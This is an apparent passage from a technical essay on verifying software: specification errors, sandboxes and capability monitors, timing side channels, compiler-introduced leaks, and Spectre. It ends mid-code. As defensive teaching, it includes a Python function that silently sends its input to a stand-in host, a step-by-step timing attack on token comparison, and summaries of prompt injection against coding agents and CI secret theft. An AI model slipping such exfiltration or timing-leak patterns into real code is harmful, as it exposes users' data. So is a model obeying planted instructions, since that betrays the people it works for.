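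**The specification itself can be wrong.** The encryption standard ML-KEM includes a step that expands a number *y* of *d* bits by rounding 3329*y*/2ᵈ to the nearest whole number. Programmers do this by adding half the divisor, 2ᵈ⁻¹, before dividing. Libcrux's formal specification added 1,664 instead, which is right for the neighbouring function that divides by 3,329. With *d* = 1, it turned 0 into 832. Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in CE Labs’ Verified Code* (2026) reports this error and a missing step in the specification of encryption. The code that users run was correct in both places.

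**Faulty or missing checks.** An attempt to prove that libcrux's code met this specification should have failed, but the project's build settings made the checker accept the relevant module without checking it. They also hid a false lemma that certain 12-bit values fit into a single bit. Cryspen's documentation listed the module containing this lemma as fully verified.

Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) describes a Lean text function that should return an empty string by its logical definition but returned the whole original string when compiled. The firm combined the two results to derive a contradiction, and from that a bogus proof of Fermat's Last Theorem. The proof needs a command that relies on Lean's compiler as well as its kernel, the small program that checks proofs. The kernel was not at fault, and Lean lists the extra assumption when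 a user asks what a theorem depends on. Lean's developers fixed the mismatch within five days.

A proof of functional correctness covers only the properties that someone stated. ImperialViolet's *We have proof automation now* (2026) describes a decompressor written in Lean for the Zstandard format. Language models took about 20 minutes to prove that its decoding tables always have the right size and structure. These theorems don't cover speed, and the decompressor is ten times slower than the standard tool. Similarly, Cryspen does not prove that compiled libcrux code does not leak secrets through its timing.

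### How much is left to read

In *The strengths and limits of formal verification* (2026), Karthikeyan Bhargavan, Cryspen's chief research scientist, responds to the criticism by arguing that proofs eliminate whole classes of bugs from large parts of a program, so reviewers can concentrate on the rest. His best evidence is HACL*, an older library whose code runs in Firefox and Linux. It has 135,000 lines of C and assembly code generated from verified sources, and about 1,800 lines of unverified C. In nine years, its developers twice found errors in the specifications, while users more often found bugs in the unverified C.

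The other cases support him on this. Testers with no stake in the proofs, and some who were openly hostile, found few errors in code whose proofs someone had checked. The unverified part can also be small. In the systems Fonseca and colleagues studied, the bugs were in specifications and connecting code that typically came to a few hundred lines.

Reviewers may miss problems if they read only the specification and a list of assumptions. They would have had to read libcrux's build settings to learn that some of its proofs never ran. Specifications can also mislead careful readers. Fonseca and colleagues admit that they did not notice at first that IronFleet's specification allowed repeated requests. Chechik, Kang and colleagues wrote in *Specification Engineering*, after a September 2025 seminar on the subject, that little is understood about what makes a specification correct or how to check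 it against what users want.

Fonseca and colleagues built a tool that disables random pieces of a program and reruns the verifier. If the program still passes, the specification does not require whatever those pieces did. In three of IronFleet's functions, the tool needed averages of 377, 18 and 8,015 attempts to disable the filter for repeated requests without failing verification. The same method would flag the `memset` line in the password example, because a proof about the returned hash succeeds with or without it. A reviewer could then decide whether the line matters. But the method cannot reveal a safeguard missing from both the specification and the code. For instance, the standard that hpke-rs implements requires a program to stop if a shared secret is all zeros. The library lacked this check, and Kobeissi's firm found the omission by comparing the code with the standard.

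## Unwanted network and file access

The function below removes surplus spaces from a text. It also sends the text to a server (the address is invented).

```python
from urllib.request import urlopen

def tidy(text):
    urlopen("https://collector.example", data=text.encode())
    return " ".join(text.split())
```

On a computer with a network connection, every test that compares the return value with the right answer passes. Without a connection, `urlopen` raises an error and the function crashes, so a developer will notice something wrong. A few more lines of code that ignore the error would prevent the crash and hide the problem.

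Coding agents can cause the same problem while they work. *Aletheia* (Shi, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that has to rename a function in a project where an attacker has planted an instruction to upload an archive to an unrelated server. The agent can rename the function and also upload the archive, and the function still passes all its tests.

The rule that `tidy` breaks is short: the function must not use the network. Some programs need a looser rule. A text editor may have good reason to download updates when it starts and to open private documents afterwards. Clarkson and Schneider give a rule that allows this: a system may not write to the network after reading from a file. Formally, it is the set of traces

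NRW = {*t* | ¬(∃ *i*, *j*: *i* < *j* ∧ isFileRead(*t*[*i*]) ∧ isNetworkWrite(*t*[*j*]))}

Here *t*[*i*] is the state at step *i* of the run *t*, isFileRead is true of states where the program reads a file, and isNetworkWrite is true of states where it sends something over the network. A run is acceptable if the program never sends anything over the network after reading a file. This rule is a single-run property. It is also a safety property, because nothing later in the run can undo a message that has been sent.

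### Stopping the program when it breaks the rule

*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) turns this rule into a monitor with two states. The monitor starts in the state "no file read", which permits every action. The first file read moves it to "file read", which permits everything except sending. Before each step of the program, the monitor checks whether its current state permits that step, and stops the program if it doesn't. An ordinary permission is simpler to enforce, because the monitor only compares each request with a fixed list.

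On an ordinary operating system, a program cannot open a file or a network connection without a system call, which is a request to the kernel. The processor already interrupts the program at that point, so a check there adds little delay. Checking every machine instruction would be slow and is rarely necessary.

System-call filters work this way. Alhindi and Hallett (2024), in *Sandboxing Adoption in Open Source Ecosystems*, compare several. For Linux's Seccomp, the reviewer writes a list of permitted calls, if necessary with conditions on their arguments. OpenBSD has a simpler filter called Pledge, which needs only one line for a program that formats text:

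```c
pledge("stdio", NULL);
```

This leaves the program 69 system calls, mostly for reading its standard input and writing its standard output. The kernel ends the program if it tries to open a connection. Seccomp cannot check a file's path, because the system call contains only the path's memory address, and the program could change the path after the check. Linux's Landlock and OpenBSD's Unveil restrict access by directory instead. The main drawback of all these filters is that developers often have to restructure a program to fit them. The filters also apply to a whole process, so they cannot stop `tidy` from using the network if the rest of the program needs it.

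A container gives a group of programs its own view of the file system and the network. The reviewer writes a configuration that lists the directories the programs can see, the ones they can change and the connections they can make. The kernel enforces this configuration, and a proxy outside the container can check the address of each outgoing connection. Anthropic's *Sandboxing* describes a similar arrangement for its coding agent, Claude Code. This arrangement restricts both files and connections, because an agent influenced by an attacker could otherwise send out private keys or alter system files to gain network access.

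WebAssembly is a format for compiled programs that has no instructions for opening files or network connections. A WebAssembly module can call only the functions that the surrounding program supplies, so the reviewer writes a list of these functions. Developers have to compile their code to this format, and the checks that keep a module within its own memory can slow it down. Schneider describes an older technique, software fault isolation, in which a tool inserts such checks into ordinary compiled code before it runs, so the reviewer has to trust the tool.

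Deno, a system for running JavaScript programs, denies access to files and the network by default. The reviewer grants exceptions on the command line:

```sh
deno run --allow-net=example.com --allow-read=./data main.ts
```

Deno checks each attempt to use a file or connection, and a forbidden attempt produces an error that the program can handle. According to Deno's *Security and permissions*, all code on the same thread has the same permissions, so `tidy` would share those of the program that calls it. A program can bypass the other permissions if it has either `--allow-run`, which lets it start other programs outside the sandbox, or `--allow-ffi`, which lets it load compiled libraries that make system calls directly.

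Deno also offers two ways to approximate the rule about file reads and network writes. A program can give up its network permission before it opens a file, but the reviewer then has to find the line that does this and check that it comes early enough. Or Deno can send every permission request to a separate program, which could run Schneider's two-state monitor. Either way, somebody has to make sure that the program cannot keep sending through a connection it opened before reading the file. Schneider warns of this kind of gap, because a system may have many ways to send a message, some of them buried deep inside it, and the rule has to cover them all.

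In a system of object capabilities, code can use a file or connection only if it holds a reference to it, so a reviewer reads a function's parameters to see what it can access. A function `tidy(text)` receives only a text and cannot reach the network, while `save(text, file)` can write to the file it receives. Python does not enforce this, since any function can import a network library. FreeBSD's Capsicum enforces something similar for whole processes. After a process calls `cap_enter`, it can no longer open files by name and has to work with those it already holds, which the developer can limit to reading. Developers again have to restructure their code so that callers pass in every resource. McClintock and Dethridge, in *Bringing Capslock analysis to deps.dev*, recommend this design for Go packages, so that a package needs few permissions of its own.

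### Checking the code before it runs

Some languages include a function's effects in its type. Ferrous Systems, a Rust consultancy, gives an example in the research language Koka. A function that prints a greeting but declares no effects does not compile until the developer adds `console` to its type. For `tidy`, the reviewer would require the type `total`, which means the function has no effects, and the compiler would reject the version that contacts a server. This check needs no monitor and adds no run-time overhead, but the language has to support it. Ferrous Systems thinks that adding effects to Rust would amount to creating a new language.

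Some tools for existing languages report which packages can reach the network or the disk. Google (2023) released one for Go, called Capslock, arguing that reading every line of a program's dependencies is an immense task. Capslock follows the calls from each function, through all its dependencies, to the standard library functions that open files, make connections or start programs. Capslock's *Know what your dependencies can do* mentions a date formatter with network access as something that deserves a closer look. `tidy` would stand out for the same reason.

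A tool can enforce a capability report by blocking new code that changes it. With git-pkgs' *capcheck* (2026), a developer saves the project's current list of capabilities, and the build fails if the code or a dependency gains a new one. This should be rare, since McClintock and Dethridge found that fewer than 2% of version updates add a capability.

These reports can overstate or understate what a package does. Google's *Caveats* explains that Capslock assumes every branch of a function can run, so it may report a file access that never happens. It cannot follow calls into C code or other programs, so it lists their use as a separate capability. The reviewer then knows only that the package may run code Capslock has not examined. In Go, 9% of packages have an indirect dependency that can start other programs.

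In *GoLeash*, Cesarano, Monperrus and Natella (2025) compared Capslock with their own monitor, which traces each system call to the Go package responsible. They took packages that were active during test runs and inserted code that sends system data to a server. On average across five applications, the monitor's detection rate was 65 percentage points higher than Capslock's. One reason is that Capslock's categories are coarser and, for instance, do not separate reading files from writing them. But Capslock also covers packages that a program includes and never runs during the tests. In Kubernetes, a large system for managing servers, it detected the inserted code in 469 of 721 packages that the monitor could not assess.

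### What a monitor cannot enforce

Schneider proved that a monitor that watches one run and can only stop it is limited to safety properties. The argument has three steps:

- The monitor has access to one run, so it has to judge that run by itself. This excludes multi-run properties.
- The monitor cannot know what the program will do next. If the run so far is unacceptable, the monitor has to stop it, even if a later step would have put things right. In symbols, if *P* is the monitor's criterion and *m* a finite beginning, ¬*P*(*m*) ⇒ ¬*P*(*mt*) for every continuation *t*.
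- The monitor has to reject an unacceptable run after a finite number of steps, so ¬*P*(*t*) ⇒ ¬*P*(*m*) for some finite beginning *m* of *t*.

Any rule that meets all three conditions is a safety property, but not every safety property meets them, because some are beyond a monitor's control. For example, a monitor can detect that a user has waited more than five seconds, but it cannot prevent this by stopping the program, because time keeps passing. It could enforce a limit measured in program steps. Monitors that can also insert actions or hold them back can enforce somewhat more rules.

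The rule about file reads and network writes is usually meant to keep the contents of files secret. Secrecy is a multi-run property, so no such monitor can enforce it exactly. Schneider observes that monitors said to prevent leaks enforce a stricter rule that implies secrecy. If a program never sends anything after reading a file, the contents cannot affect what it sends. But the rule also stops the text editor from checking for updates once a document is open, even though the request would contain nothing from the document.

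### Leaks through permitted addresses

Many programs have to send messages after reading files, and the practical way to restrict them is to list the addresses they may contact. Suppose a text editor sends documents to an online spelling checker. If the editor also includes a password from another file, the message still goes to a permitted address, so a monitor that checks only addresses will not stop it.

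Claude Code's proxy allows or blocks connections based on the name of the requested server and does not inspect the contents of encrypted connections. Anthropic therefore warns against permitting broad domains such as github.com, where an attacker can also have an account. A program may also be able to use domain fronting to reach a different server while naming a permitted one.

Attackers have already used permitted channels on GitHub. Many projects there use GitHub Actions, which builds and tests their code automatically in jobs made up of several steps. *Granite* (Moazen, Ahmadian and Balliu, 2025) describes a March 2025 attack in which a compromised step printed passwords and keys to the projects' own logs, affecting an estimated 23,000 projects. In 2026, compromised packages took a job's access token, which had permission to change the project's files, and used it to save stolen secrets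 in the victim's own repository. A list of permitted addresses would not have prevented either attack, because the jobs needed to communicate with GitHub.

A more specific rule can narrow the channel. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes how the online version of Claude Code uses a proxy to check that the agent sends code only to the branch the user chose. The proxy keeps the real GitHub password outside the sandbox and adds it after this check, so the agent cannot leak it. The agent could still copy some other secret into a file on the permitted branch. To rule that out, somebody has to read the changes or compare runs with different secrets.

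### Broad permissions and trusted components

A large program's permissions reveal little about its individual parts. Capslock's sample report for a project with about 45 packages includes network access, file access and the ability to run other programs. All of these make sense for the project as a whole, so the summary doesn't show whether any one small package should have them.

Cesarano and colleagues compared a single list of permitted capabilities for a whole application with separate lists for each package. They inserted five kinds of malicious code into five large Go applications, one package at a time, producing 3,265 altered versions. Averaged across the applications, the single list detected 32% of the altered versions and the separate lists detected 98%.

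| Inserted behaviour | Caught by one list per application | Caught by one list per package |
|---|---|---|
| Open a remote shell for an attacker | All | All |
| Send system configuration to a server | None | 98–100% |
| Steal data from other applications | All in three applications, none in two | All |
| Load a hidden library | None | 87–99% |
| Download malicious files | None | 96–100% |

All the applications already sent data over the network, so another package that did so broke no application-wide rule. Even the successes in the middle column were partly luck, because the remote shell and the data theft also changed resource limits, a rare capability that the original applications never used.

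The separate lists took 1.3–5.1% more processor time per request, compared with 0.2–1.6% for the single list. They may also need maintenance, because the monitor builds them from recorded runs and any legitimate action missing from the recordings will raise an alarm. The researchers saw no false alarms, but they used the same workload to build the lists and to test them.

Narrow permissions can still fail if a restricted component gets a trusted one to act on its behalf, which is known as the confused deputy problem. For example, a package that handles command-line options may have no permission to send data, but an attacker who controls it could make it call a networking package that does. Cesarano and colleagues' monitor would stop this, because it checks the whole chain of calls that led to each system call. *Containing Malicious Package Updates in npm with a Lightweight Permission System*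 (2021) proposes that packages also declare the permissions that their imported packages need. An attacker then gains nothing by calling another package, but packages near the top of a large program's dependency tree are likely to need almost every permission.

An attacker may be able to misuse a trusted component without calling it. Moazen and colleagues point out that a malicious step in a GitHub job can alter files that a later step will publish with its own legitimate permission. In JavaScript, an attacker can sometimes change default values that all objects share, so that trusted code runs with settings the attacker chose. Deno's permissions reduce the damage, but *GHunter* (2024) notes that an application containing trusted code that can be exploited this way must already have been granted some of the access it needs.

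### How narrowly developers set permissions

Few developers use system-call filters directly. Alhindi and Hallett searched the packages of four operating systems in 2023 and found that the share using these filters directly ranged from 0.14% on FreeBSD to 1.48% on OpenBSD. Between 17% and 45% depended on a package that did, though sometimes only for a minor function. No package used Landlock to build a sandbox. Developers who used Seccomp were fairly careful. About 80% of their packages on both Linux systems restricted the arguments of calls as well as the calls themselves.

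Permissions on GitHub are also often too broad. Moazen and colleagues examined 12,915 jobs from popular projects and classed 46.3% as overprivileged. GitHub sets permissions for a whole job, so a step that only lists changed files may also be able to approve changes. Their tool sets permissions for each step instead. In the overprivileged jobs they tested, the tool removed write access from about 83% of the steps that had it and made steps 7.9% slower on average.

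According to its documentation, Claude Code's sandbox by default lets commands change files only in the current project but read almost every file on the computer. A malicious command could therefore read private files elsewhere and send them to any permitted address, unless the user excludes those files. If the sandbox cannot start, Claude Code by default warns the user and runs commands without it. Relying on users to approve every command may still be worse, because they stop paying attention. Anthropic introduced the sandbox partly for this reason, and in its internal use the sandbox reduced approval requests by 84%.

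Strict limits can make agents less successful and more expensive to run, which may explain some of the broad permissions. In *Permission Denied*, Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026) tested twelve coding agents on 89 tasks, with and without strict limits on files, connections and administrator rights. Under the limits, success rates fell by 7 to 18 percentage points and costs per task rose by 16% to 167%. Seven tasks became impossible because they required something the limits forbade. The agents discovered the limits only when a command failed, so telling them the rules in advance might have saved some of the cost.

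Shi and colleagues' tool, Aletheia, automatically searches for unnecessary permissions. It lists the permissions requested in a project's instructions to an agent, removes one, and has the agent repeat the task in a sandbox. If the result still passes the functional tests, the task did not need the permission. In the renaming example, the agent succeeds without access to the attacker's server, so Aletheia flags the upload. It detected all 314 malicious instruction files in a test collection and wrongly flagged 3 of 85 harmless ones, at an average cost of 22 cents per file.

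With this method, the tests must cover everything the program legitimately needs to do, though they no longer have to detect the upload. If a program sends a monthly backup to another server and no test covers this, the permission for the backup will also look unnecessary.

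## Timing and other side channels

A sandbox can deny a program all access to files and the network, but it does not hide how long the program takes to run. Running time is the best-known side channel, an effect other than the program's intended output that leaks information. Others include the memory addresses a program reads, which another program on the same machine can sometimes infer, and the processor's power use, which an attacker can measure with equipment close to the device.

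### Guessing a token one byte at a time

Many web services give each user a token, a random value that the user's software sends with every request. Suppose that tokens are 16 bytes long and a server checks them with this function:

```python
def same(token, guess):
    if len(token) != len(guess):
        return False
    for t, g in zip(token, guess):
        if t != g:
            return False
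    return True
```

The function returns the right answer for every pair of inputs, so it passes every functional test. There are 2¹²⁸ possible tokens, so an attacker who saw only the function's answers could not feasibly guess the right one. But the loop stops at the first wrong byte, so a guess takes slightly longer if its first byte is right. The attacker can send 256 guesses that differ only in the first byte, keep the byte that took longest, and repeat this for each byte until the last, which the function's answer reveals. The attack takes at most 16 × 256 = 4,096 guesses.

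The timing difference may be only billionths of a second, so the attacker has to repeat each guess and average the times. If 1,000 repetitions are enough, the attack takes about 4.1 million requests, or 68 minutes at 1,000 requests a second.

The following version removes the early exit:

```python
def same(token, guess):
    if len(token) != len(guess):
        return False
    difference = 0
    for t, g in zip(token, guess):
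        difference |= t ^ g
    return difference == 0
```

The expression `t ^ g` is zero if the two bytes are equal, and `|=` records every bit in which any pair differs. The loop now runs 16 times regardless of the guess. Both versions meet the same functional specification and pass the same tests.

A coding agent made a related mistake in Django, a widely used web framework. Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Is Vibe Coding Safe?*, asked an agent running Claude 4 Sonnet to write Django's `verify_password()`, which compares a typed password with the stored, scrambled one. Scrambling is deliberately slow, to hinder anyone who steals the stored passwords. When an account has no usable password, the function has nothing to compare, but the secure version does a fake comparison anyway so that the refusal takes about as long as usual. The agent's version refused immediately. The refusal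 was correct, but an attacker could learn from its unusual speed that the username exists, and then target its owner with phishing or passwords stolen elsewhere. The agent's instructions had included a general reminder to avoid common vulnerabilities.

This is a single case from a 2025 model. Zhao and colleagues group their results into broad categories, such as cryptographic failures, and no one seems to have published a count yet of how often AI-written cryptographic code leaks information through timing.

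### A rule that compares two runs

A rule about running time itself would be hard to check, because the time depends on the processor and on whatever else the machine is doing. Developers use a leakage model instead, which is an assumption about which effects of a computation an attacker can observe. Let ℓ(*p*, *s*) be the sequence of observations that the model grants the attacker when a program runs with public input *p* and secret *s*. The program is constant-time in this model if

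ℓ(*p*, *s*) = ℓ(*p*, *s*′) for all *p*, *s* and *s*′.

Constant-time execution is a form of noninterference, so detecting a violation requires comparing two runs. In the usual model, the attacker sees the direction of every branch and the address of every memory access. In a stricter model, the attacker also sees the operands of instructions whose duration depends on them. *Systematic Timing Leakage Analysis of NIST PQDSS Candidates* (Adjonyo, Bardin and colleagues, 2025) gives as examples division on many processors and a multiplication instruction on ARM's Cortex-M3. The KyberSlash attack used the timing of divisions against implementations of Kyber, the scheme on which the ML-KEM standard is based.

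Suppose the attacker's guess starts with the bytes 7A 00. If the token starts with 7A 31, the first version of `same` finds a difference at the second byte. If the token starts with 5B, the function finds a difference at the first byte. The two runs take different sequences of branches, so this version is not constant-time. In the second version, the loop takes the same sequence of branches for every token. As with the password function, the rule should apply only to pairs of runs that return the same answer.

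The model includes memory addresses because a processor keeps recently used data in a small, fast memory called a cache. Another program on the same machine can time its own memory accesses, and the times may reveal which entry of a table the first program read. Programmers prevent this by writing code that reads every entry of the table and selects the right one by arithmetic.

Despite its name, constant-time code may take longer for a longer message, as long as the length is public. The rule against branching on secrets can also be stricter than necessary. Django's secure function branches on whether an account has a usable password, which breaks the rule if that fact is secret. Both branches take about the same time, so an attacker who can time only whole responses would learn little, though one who can run programs on the server might learn more.

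### Four ways of checking

Adjonyo and colleagues applied several kinds of checkers to candidates for a signature standard meant to resist quantum computers. NIST, the US standards agency, is choosing the standard and expects candidates to resist timing attacks. The researchers examined 302 variants of 15 schemes. They checked only the function that signs a message and treated the private key as the secret.

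The most direct check is to time the program. A tool called dudect runs it many times with two groups of secrets and applies Welch's *t*-test to the running times:

*t* = (*m*₁ − *m*₂) / √(*v*₁/*n*₁ + *v*₂/*n*₂)

Here *m*₁ and *m*₂ are the mean times of the two groups, *v*₁ and *v*₂ their variances, and *n*₁ and *n*₂ the numbers of runs. If *t* is far from zero, the time probably depends on the secret. Adjonyo and colleagues took 210,000 measurements by default. They grouped the keys by one bit at a time, using a bit near the start of the key, one in the middle and one at the end.

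Timing tests need no leakage model and include the effects of the real processor. But they do not show which line of code is responsible, and they can miss a leak that is small compared with the noise or that depends on other bits of the key. They measure only the total time, whereas some attackers can observe individual instructions. They can also raise false alarms. The researchers set a second timing tool, RTLF, to a false-alarm rate of 9%. If its three tests of a scheme were independent, a scheme without leaks would have about a 25% chance of at least one false alarm.

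Valgrind, a tool that finds uses of uninitialised memory (memory to which a program has not yet written a value), can also be used to find timing leaks. It tracks uninitialised values through calculations and warns if a branch or a memory address depends on one. The constant-time rule forbids the same two uses of secrets, so the programmer Adam Langley had the idea of marking a secret key as uninitialised and running the program as usual. One run can be enough to find a leak, because Valgrind tracks which values depend on the key and doesn't need to compare runs. TIMECOP, which automates the method, misses leaks in code that the run does not reach.

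A proof can cover all inputs. Self-composition works here if the combined program compares the branches and addresses of the two copies as well as their outputs. Tools for such proofs usually analyse the source code or an intermediate form of it. For example, the verified library HACL\* has a proof that its source code is constant-time, but the proof does not cover what an ordinary compiler does to that code.

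Binary analysis checks the compiled program instead. Binsec/Rel2 follows two copies of the machine code with symbols in place of the secret bytes. At each branch and memory access, it checks whether different secrets could make the copies behave differently, and if so, produces an example. It can prove a program constant-time up to a certain number of instructions, but Adjonyo and colleagues used it only to find bugs. They treated a single byte of the key as secret, fixed the public inputs and stopped after 30 minutes, so the absence of an alert doesn't prove that a scheme is constant-time.

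The researchers sorted through the alerts by hand and reported the 26 most serious issues to the schemes' developers, who had fixed five by the time of publication. Two of the five were in LESS, and the others were in SNOVA, Preon and Mirath. Cryptography specialists had written all of this code for a competition that judges resistance to such attacks.

The sorting was necessary because many alerts were harmless, and a person who knows the cryptographic scheme has to decide which ones matter. In a small sample that the researchers checked by hand, 67% of TIMECOP's alerts were not real violations of the rule, while all of Binsec/Rel2's alerts were real violations. Some alerts were irrelevant because a private key often contains public parts, and the tools treated the whole key as secret. Others were irrelevant because some schemes draw random values and discard those that do not fit. The number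 of attempts then depends on secret data, but it usually reveals information only about the discarded values.

### How compilers reintroduce leaks

Most cryptographic libraries rely on careful source code and an ordinary compiler. The compiler has to preserve the program's results, but not its branches or memory accesses. Suppose a program has to choose between two values according to a secret bit. An `if` statement would branch on the secret, so cryptographers use arithmetic:

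```c
uint32_t choose(uint32_t x, uint32_t y, uint32_t bit) {
    uint32_t mask = -bit;    // 32 ones if bit is 1, 32 zeros if bit is 0
    return (x & mask) | (y & ~mask);
}
```

If `bit` is 1, `x & mask` equals `x` and `y & ~mask` is zero, so the function returns `x`. If `bit` is 0, it returns `y`. The source code contains no branch.

LLVM, which underlies the C compiler Clang and many others, can recognise this pattern as a choice between two values and replace the arithmetic with an internal instruction called `select`. On 64-bit Intel-type processors, LLVM often turns `select` into a conditional move, which takes the same time whichever value it picks. On RISC-V processors, it may produce a branch. On some ARM processors, it may compute the address of the chosen value and read from there, which makes the address depend on the secret. *Breaking Bad* (Schneider, Lain and colleagues, 2024)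 reports both kinds of leak in compiled versions of HACL\*, despite the proof about its source code.

The study covered eight cryptographic libraries and six types of processor. The researchers compiled the libraries with GCC 5 to 13 and LLVM 5 to 18 at up to seven optimisation levels. An emulator, which imitates each processor in software, then ran every algorithm eight times and recorded the branches taken and the memory addresses accessed. The random numbers were fixed, so any difference between runs with different keys had to come from the keys. Of 44,604 planned experiments, 37,818 finished. Among 5,716 binaries, 429 (7.5%) had at least one secret-dependent branch that the compiler had introduced, and 368 (6.4%) had at least one secret-dependent memory access. The leaks occurred in five of the eight libraries.

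These percentages cover a deliberately wide range of compilers and processors, so they do not show how many programs in use have such leaks. The researchers also did not assess how many of the leaks an attacker could exploit. They removed leaks already present in the source code partly by hand and may have missed some, which could make the percentages too high. The percentages could also be too low, because eight runs can overlook leaks that only rare keys reveal.

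Leaks were more common on MIPS, RISC-V and 32-bit x86 processors, but the most widely used types had them too. When compiling BearSSL's RSA encryption code for 64-bit x86, LLVM used a conditional move to choose an address that the program then read from. Switching off optimisation reduced the number of leaks but did not eliminate them. GCC still sometimes made the Botan library skip an addition when the number to be added was zero.

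Reading the source code is a poor way to find these leaks. One widely used routine that relies on mask arithmetic passed the tests with every compiler. But when the researchers made harmless-looking changes, such as moving the selection into its own function, compilers introduced leaks again. They found no way to tell from the source code alone whether a pattern was safe.

In *Fun with flags*, Geimer and Maurice (2025) traced such leaks to individual optimisation steps. They compiled the same code with an older and a newer version of each compiler (LLVM 12 and 18, GCC 9 and 13), because a leak that appears with only one version must come from the compiler. They ran each binary with 16 random secrets and matched every leak to a line of source code. The newer compilers added only a few leaks, mostly in LLVM.

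One of these leaks, also in BearSSL's RSA code, shows how optimisation steps can interact. The code reads every entry of a table and keeps the right one with a mask, which LLVM 18 turned into a `select` inside a loop. The next step moved the `select` out of the loop and made it a branch. When Geimer and Maurice disabled this step, another, which makes code process several numbers at once, produced a branch instead. When they disabled that too, a third step replaced a conditional move with a jump. The program became constant-time only with all three disabled.

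Developers can disable these steps with compiler flags. In Geimer and Maurice's tests, the flags removed every leak that the compilers had added to constant-time source code:

| Library | Average slowdown with LLVM 18 | Average slowdown with GCC 13 |
|---|---|---|
| BearSSL | 3.3% | 0.4% |
| MbedTLS | 0.7% | 1.1% |

Geimer and Maurice do not consider these slowdowns significant because the results varied so much between operations. The flags are therefore a precaution that a cryptographic library can take with little apparent loss of speed. But the tests covered only 64-bit Intel-type processors, some of the LLVM flags are undocumented, and a later compiler version may add a step that the flags do not disable.

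Stronger guarantees are available, but they have drawbacks. A version of the verified compiler CompCert is proven to keep constant-time code constant-time, but it supports fewer processors than ordinary compilers and produces slower programs. Developers can also write critical functions in assembly language, but must do so separately for each type of processor.

### A constant-time operation for LLVM

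In August 2025, the security firm Trail of Bits proposed a way for programmers to tell LLVM which choices must stay constant-time. Instead of mask arithmetic, they would write

```c
result = __builtin_ct_select(condition, a, b);
```

and LLVM would keep this operation out of the optimisations that can turn it into a branch. At the end, it would produce a conditional move or an equivalent instruction where the processor has one, and mask arithmetic elsewhere. According to Trail of Bits' *Introducing constant-time support for LLVM to protect cryptographic code*, early tests with the *Breaking Bad* test suite found that code using the operation stayed constant-time at every optimisation level tested.

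The proposal covers only branches, not leaks through the cache or division, and programmers still have to find every place where they need the operation. In the discussion of Trail of Bits' *[RFC] Constant-Time Coding Support*, several developers preferred a "secret" type for variables. The compiler would report an error if a program branched on a secret, whether the programmer or an optimisation step had introduced the branch. This would come close to putting the two-run rule into the programming language. Trail of Bits replied that it would mean changing the language. Another participant argued that people who write cryptography in C now face all of these problems and would be thrilled to have 99% of them solved.

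The guarantee may also be weaker on some processors than on others. Trail of Bits first planned for the compiler to report an error on any processor without specific support. It later had the compiler fall back on protected mask arithmetic instead, but acknowledged that later compilation steps might still turn some patterns into branches, for example on RISC-V. The compiler would not warn a programmer who relied on the operation's name.

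LLVM had apparently not adopted the operation by its 2026 releases. Friedman (2025), an LLVM reviewer, wrote in November that he was "still generally skeptical of this approach". In December, Trail of Bits expected the changes to appear in a future release. According to an automatic test report (LLVM, 2026), the part for C was still awaiting approval on 22 May 2026. It passed 88,045 tests and failed one, the test of the new operation itself. The release notes for LLVM 23.1 do not list the operation among the changes to the compiler's intermediate language. Many developers therefore probably still rely on assembly code, as the RustCrypto libraries do for such choices.

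### Leaks from the processor

Even a program with the right instructions can leak if the processor does something the leakage model omits. Tatham (2025), who maintains the remote-login program PuTTY, pointed out in a review of the LLVM change that the change's guarantee can depend on a processor setting. On some ARM processors, certain instructions are guaranteed to take the same time for all data only while a mode called DIT (data-independent timing) is on. Intel has a similar mode, which only the operating system can switch on. Checking the binary cannot show whether the mode will be on when the program runs.

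Frequency scaling can reveal secrets even if every instruction takes the same number of processor cycles. The number of ones in the data affects how hot the processor gets, and a processor that gets too hot lowers its clock speed, so the same cycles take longer. Adjonyo and colleagues cite work by Wang and others, who showed that an attacker can measure this slowdown and learn how many ones the secret values contain. In the usual model, two runs that differ only in their secret values would look identical, because their branches and addresses are the same.

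Speculative execution causes a different problem. To save time, a processor predicts which way a branch will go and starts on the instructions that follow. If the prediction is wrong, it discards the results, but the cache still contains whatever it loaded. Consider this code, where the attacker chooses `i`:

```c
if (i < length)
    y = table[array[i] * 64];
```

Under the rules of C, the program never reads past the end of `array`. But if `i` is too large, the processor may predict that the test will succeed, read a secret byte stored beyond the array, and use that byte to choose an address in `table`. The attacker can then find out from the cache which address was used. Spectre attacks work this way. A leakage model that covers them must include instructions that the processor starts and then discards. Trail of Bits says that its operation cannot prevent such attacks.

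Some processors also have a data memory-dependent prefetcher, which looks for values in memory that resemble addresses and loads the data at those addresses in advance. The prefetcher may use a secret as an address even if the program avoids doing so. According to a researcher in the LLVM discussion, Apple's prefetchers can act on secret data that the program never reads, if the program reads public data stored nearby. On Apple's M1 and M2 chips, the DIT setting did not switch the prefetcher off.

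The same researcher proposes that programmers mark the sections of code that handle secrets, and that the operating system switch on the necessary protections at the start of each section. An operating system update could then protect existing programs from a newly discovered hardware leak. Secret data would also be inaccessible outside these sections, even to a prefetcher.

### What a reviewer has to examine

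A reviewer can judge from the rule alone whether it names the right secrets. This is essential in the Django case, because a rule that listed only passwords as secret would have allowed the agent's function, which did not reveal anyone's password. The reviewer can also decide what the program may reveal and whether the rule should assume attackers who can run programs on the same machine. Valgrind and Binsec/Rel2 cannot make these decisions, because somebody has to tell them which data are secret.

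A person or a tool can find some violations of the rule in the source code, such as the early exit in `same`, and should look for them before anyone compiles the program. But a statement such as "this library is constant-time" is incomplete unless it names the compiler, its version and settings, and the type of processor. *Breaking Bad* recommends that each release of a library list the combinations its developers have tested. Developers should also repeat the tests after every compiler update, even if the code hasn't changed. AI-written code needs the same tests of the binary, because the compiler can add a leak no matter who wrote the source.

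For the hardware, a reviewer depends on the manufacturer's documentation and on timing tests run on the processors that the program will use. Adjonyo and colleagues call statistical tests a "last line of defense" because they can detect effects that no model includes. A program can still pass these tests and be vulnerable to an effect that nobody has discovered yet. Spectre, for example, was unknown when seL4's developers finished their confidentiality proof. A reviewer should therefore expect to revise the leakage model while the program is in use.

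## Performance and resource use

A program's running time matters even when it reveals no secrets, because users have to wait and somebody has to pay for the machine. The two functions below both sort a list:

```python
from heapq import merge

def swap_sort(items):
    items = list(items)
    for _ in range(len(items)):
        for j in range(len(items) - 1):
            if items[j] > items[j + 1]:
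                items[j], items[j + 1] = items[j + 1], items[j]
    return items

def merge_sort(items):
    if len(items) < 2:
        return list(items)
    half = len(items) // 2
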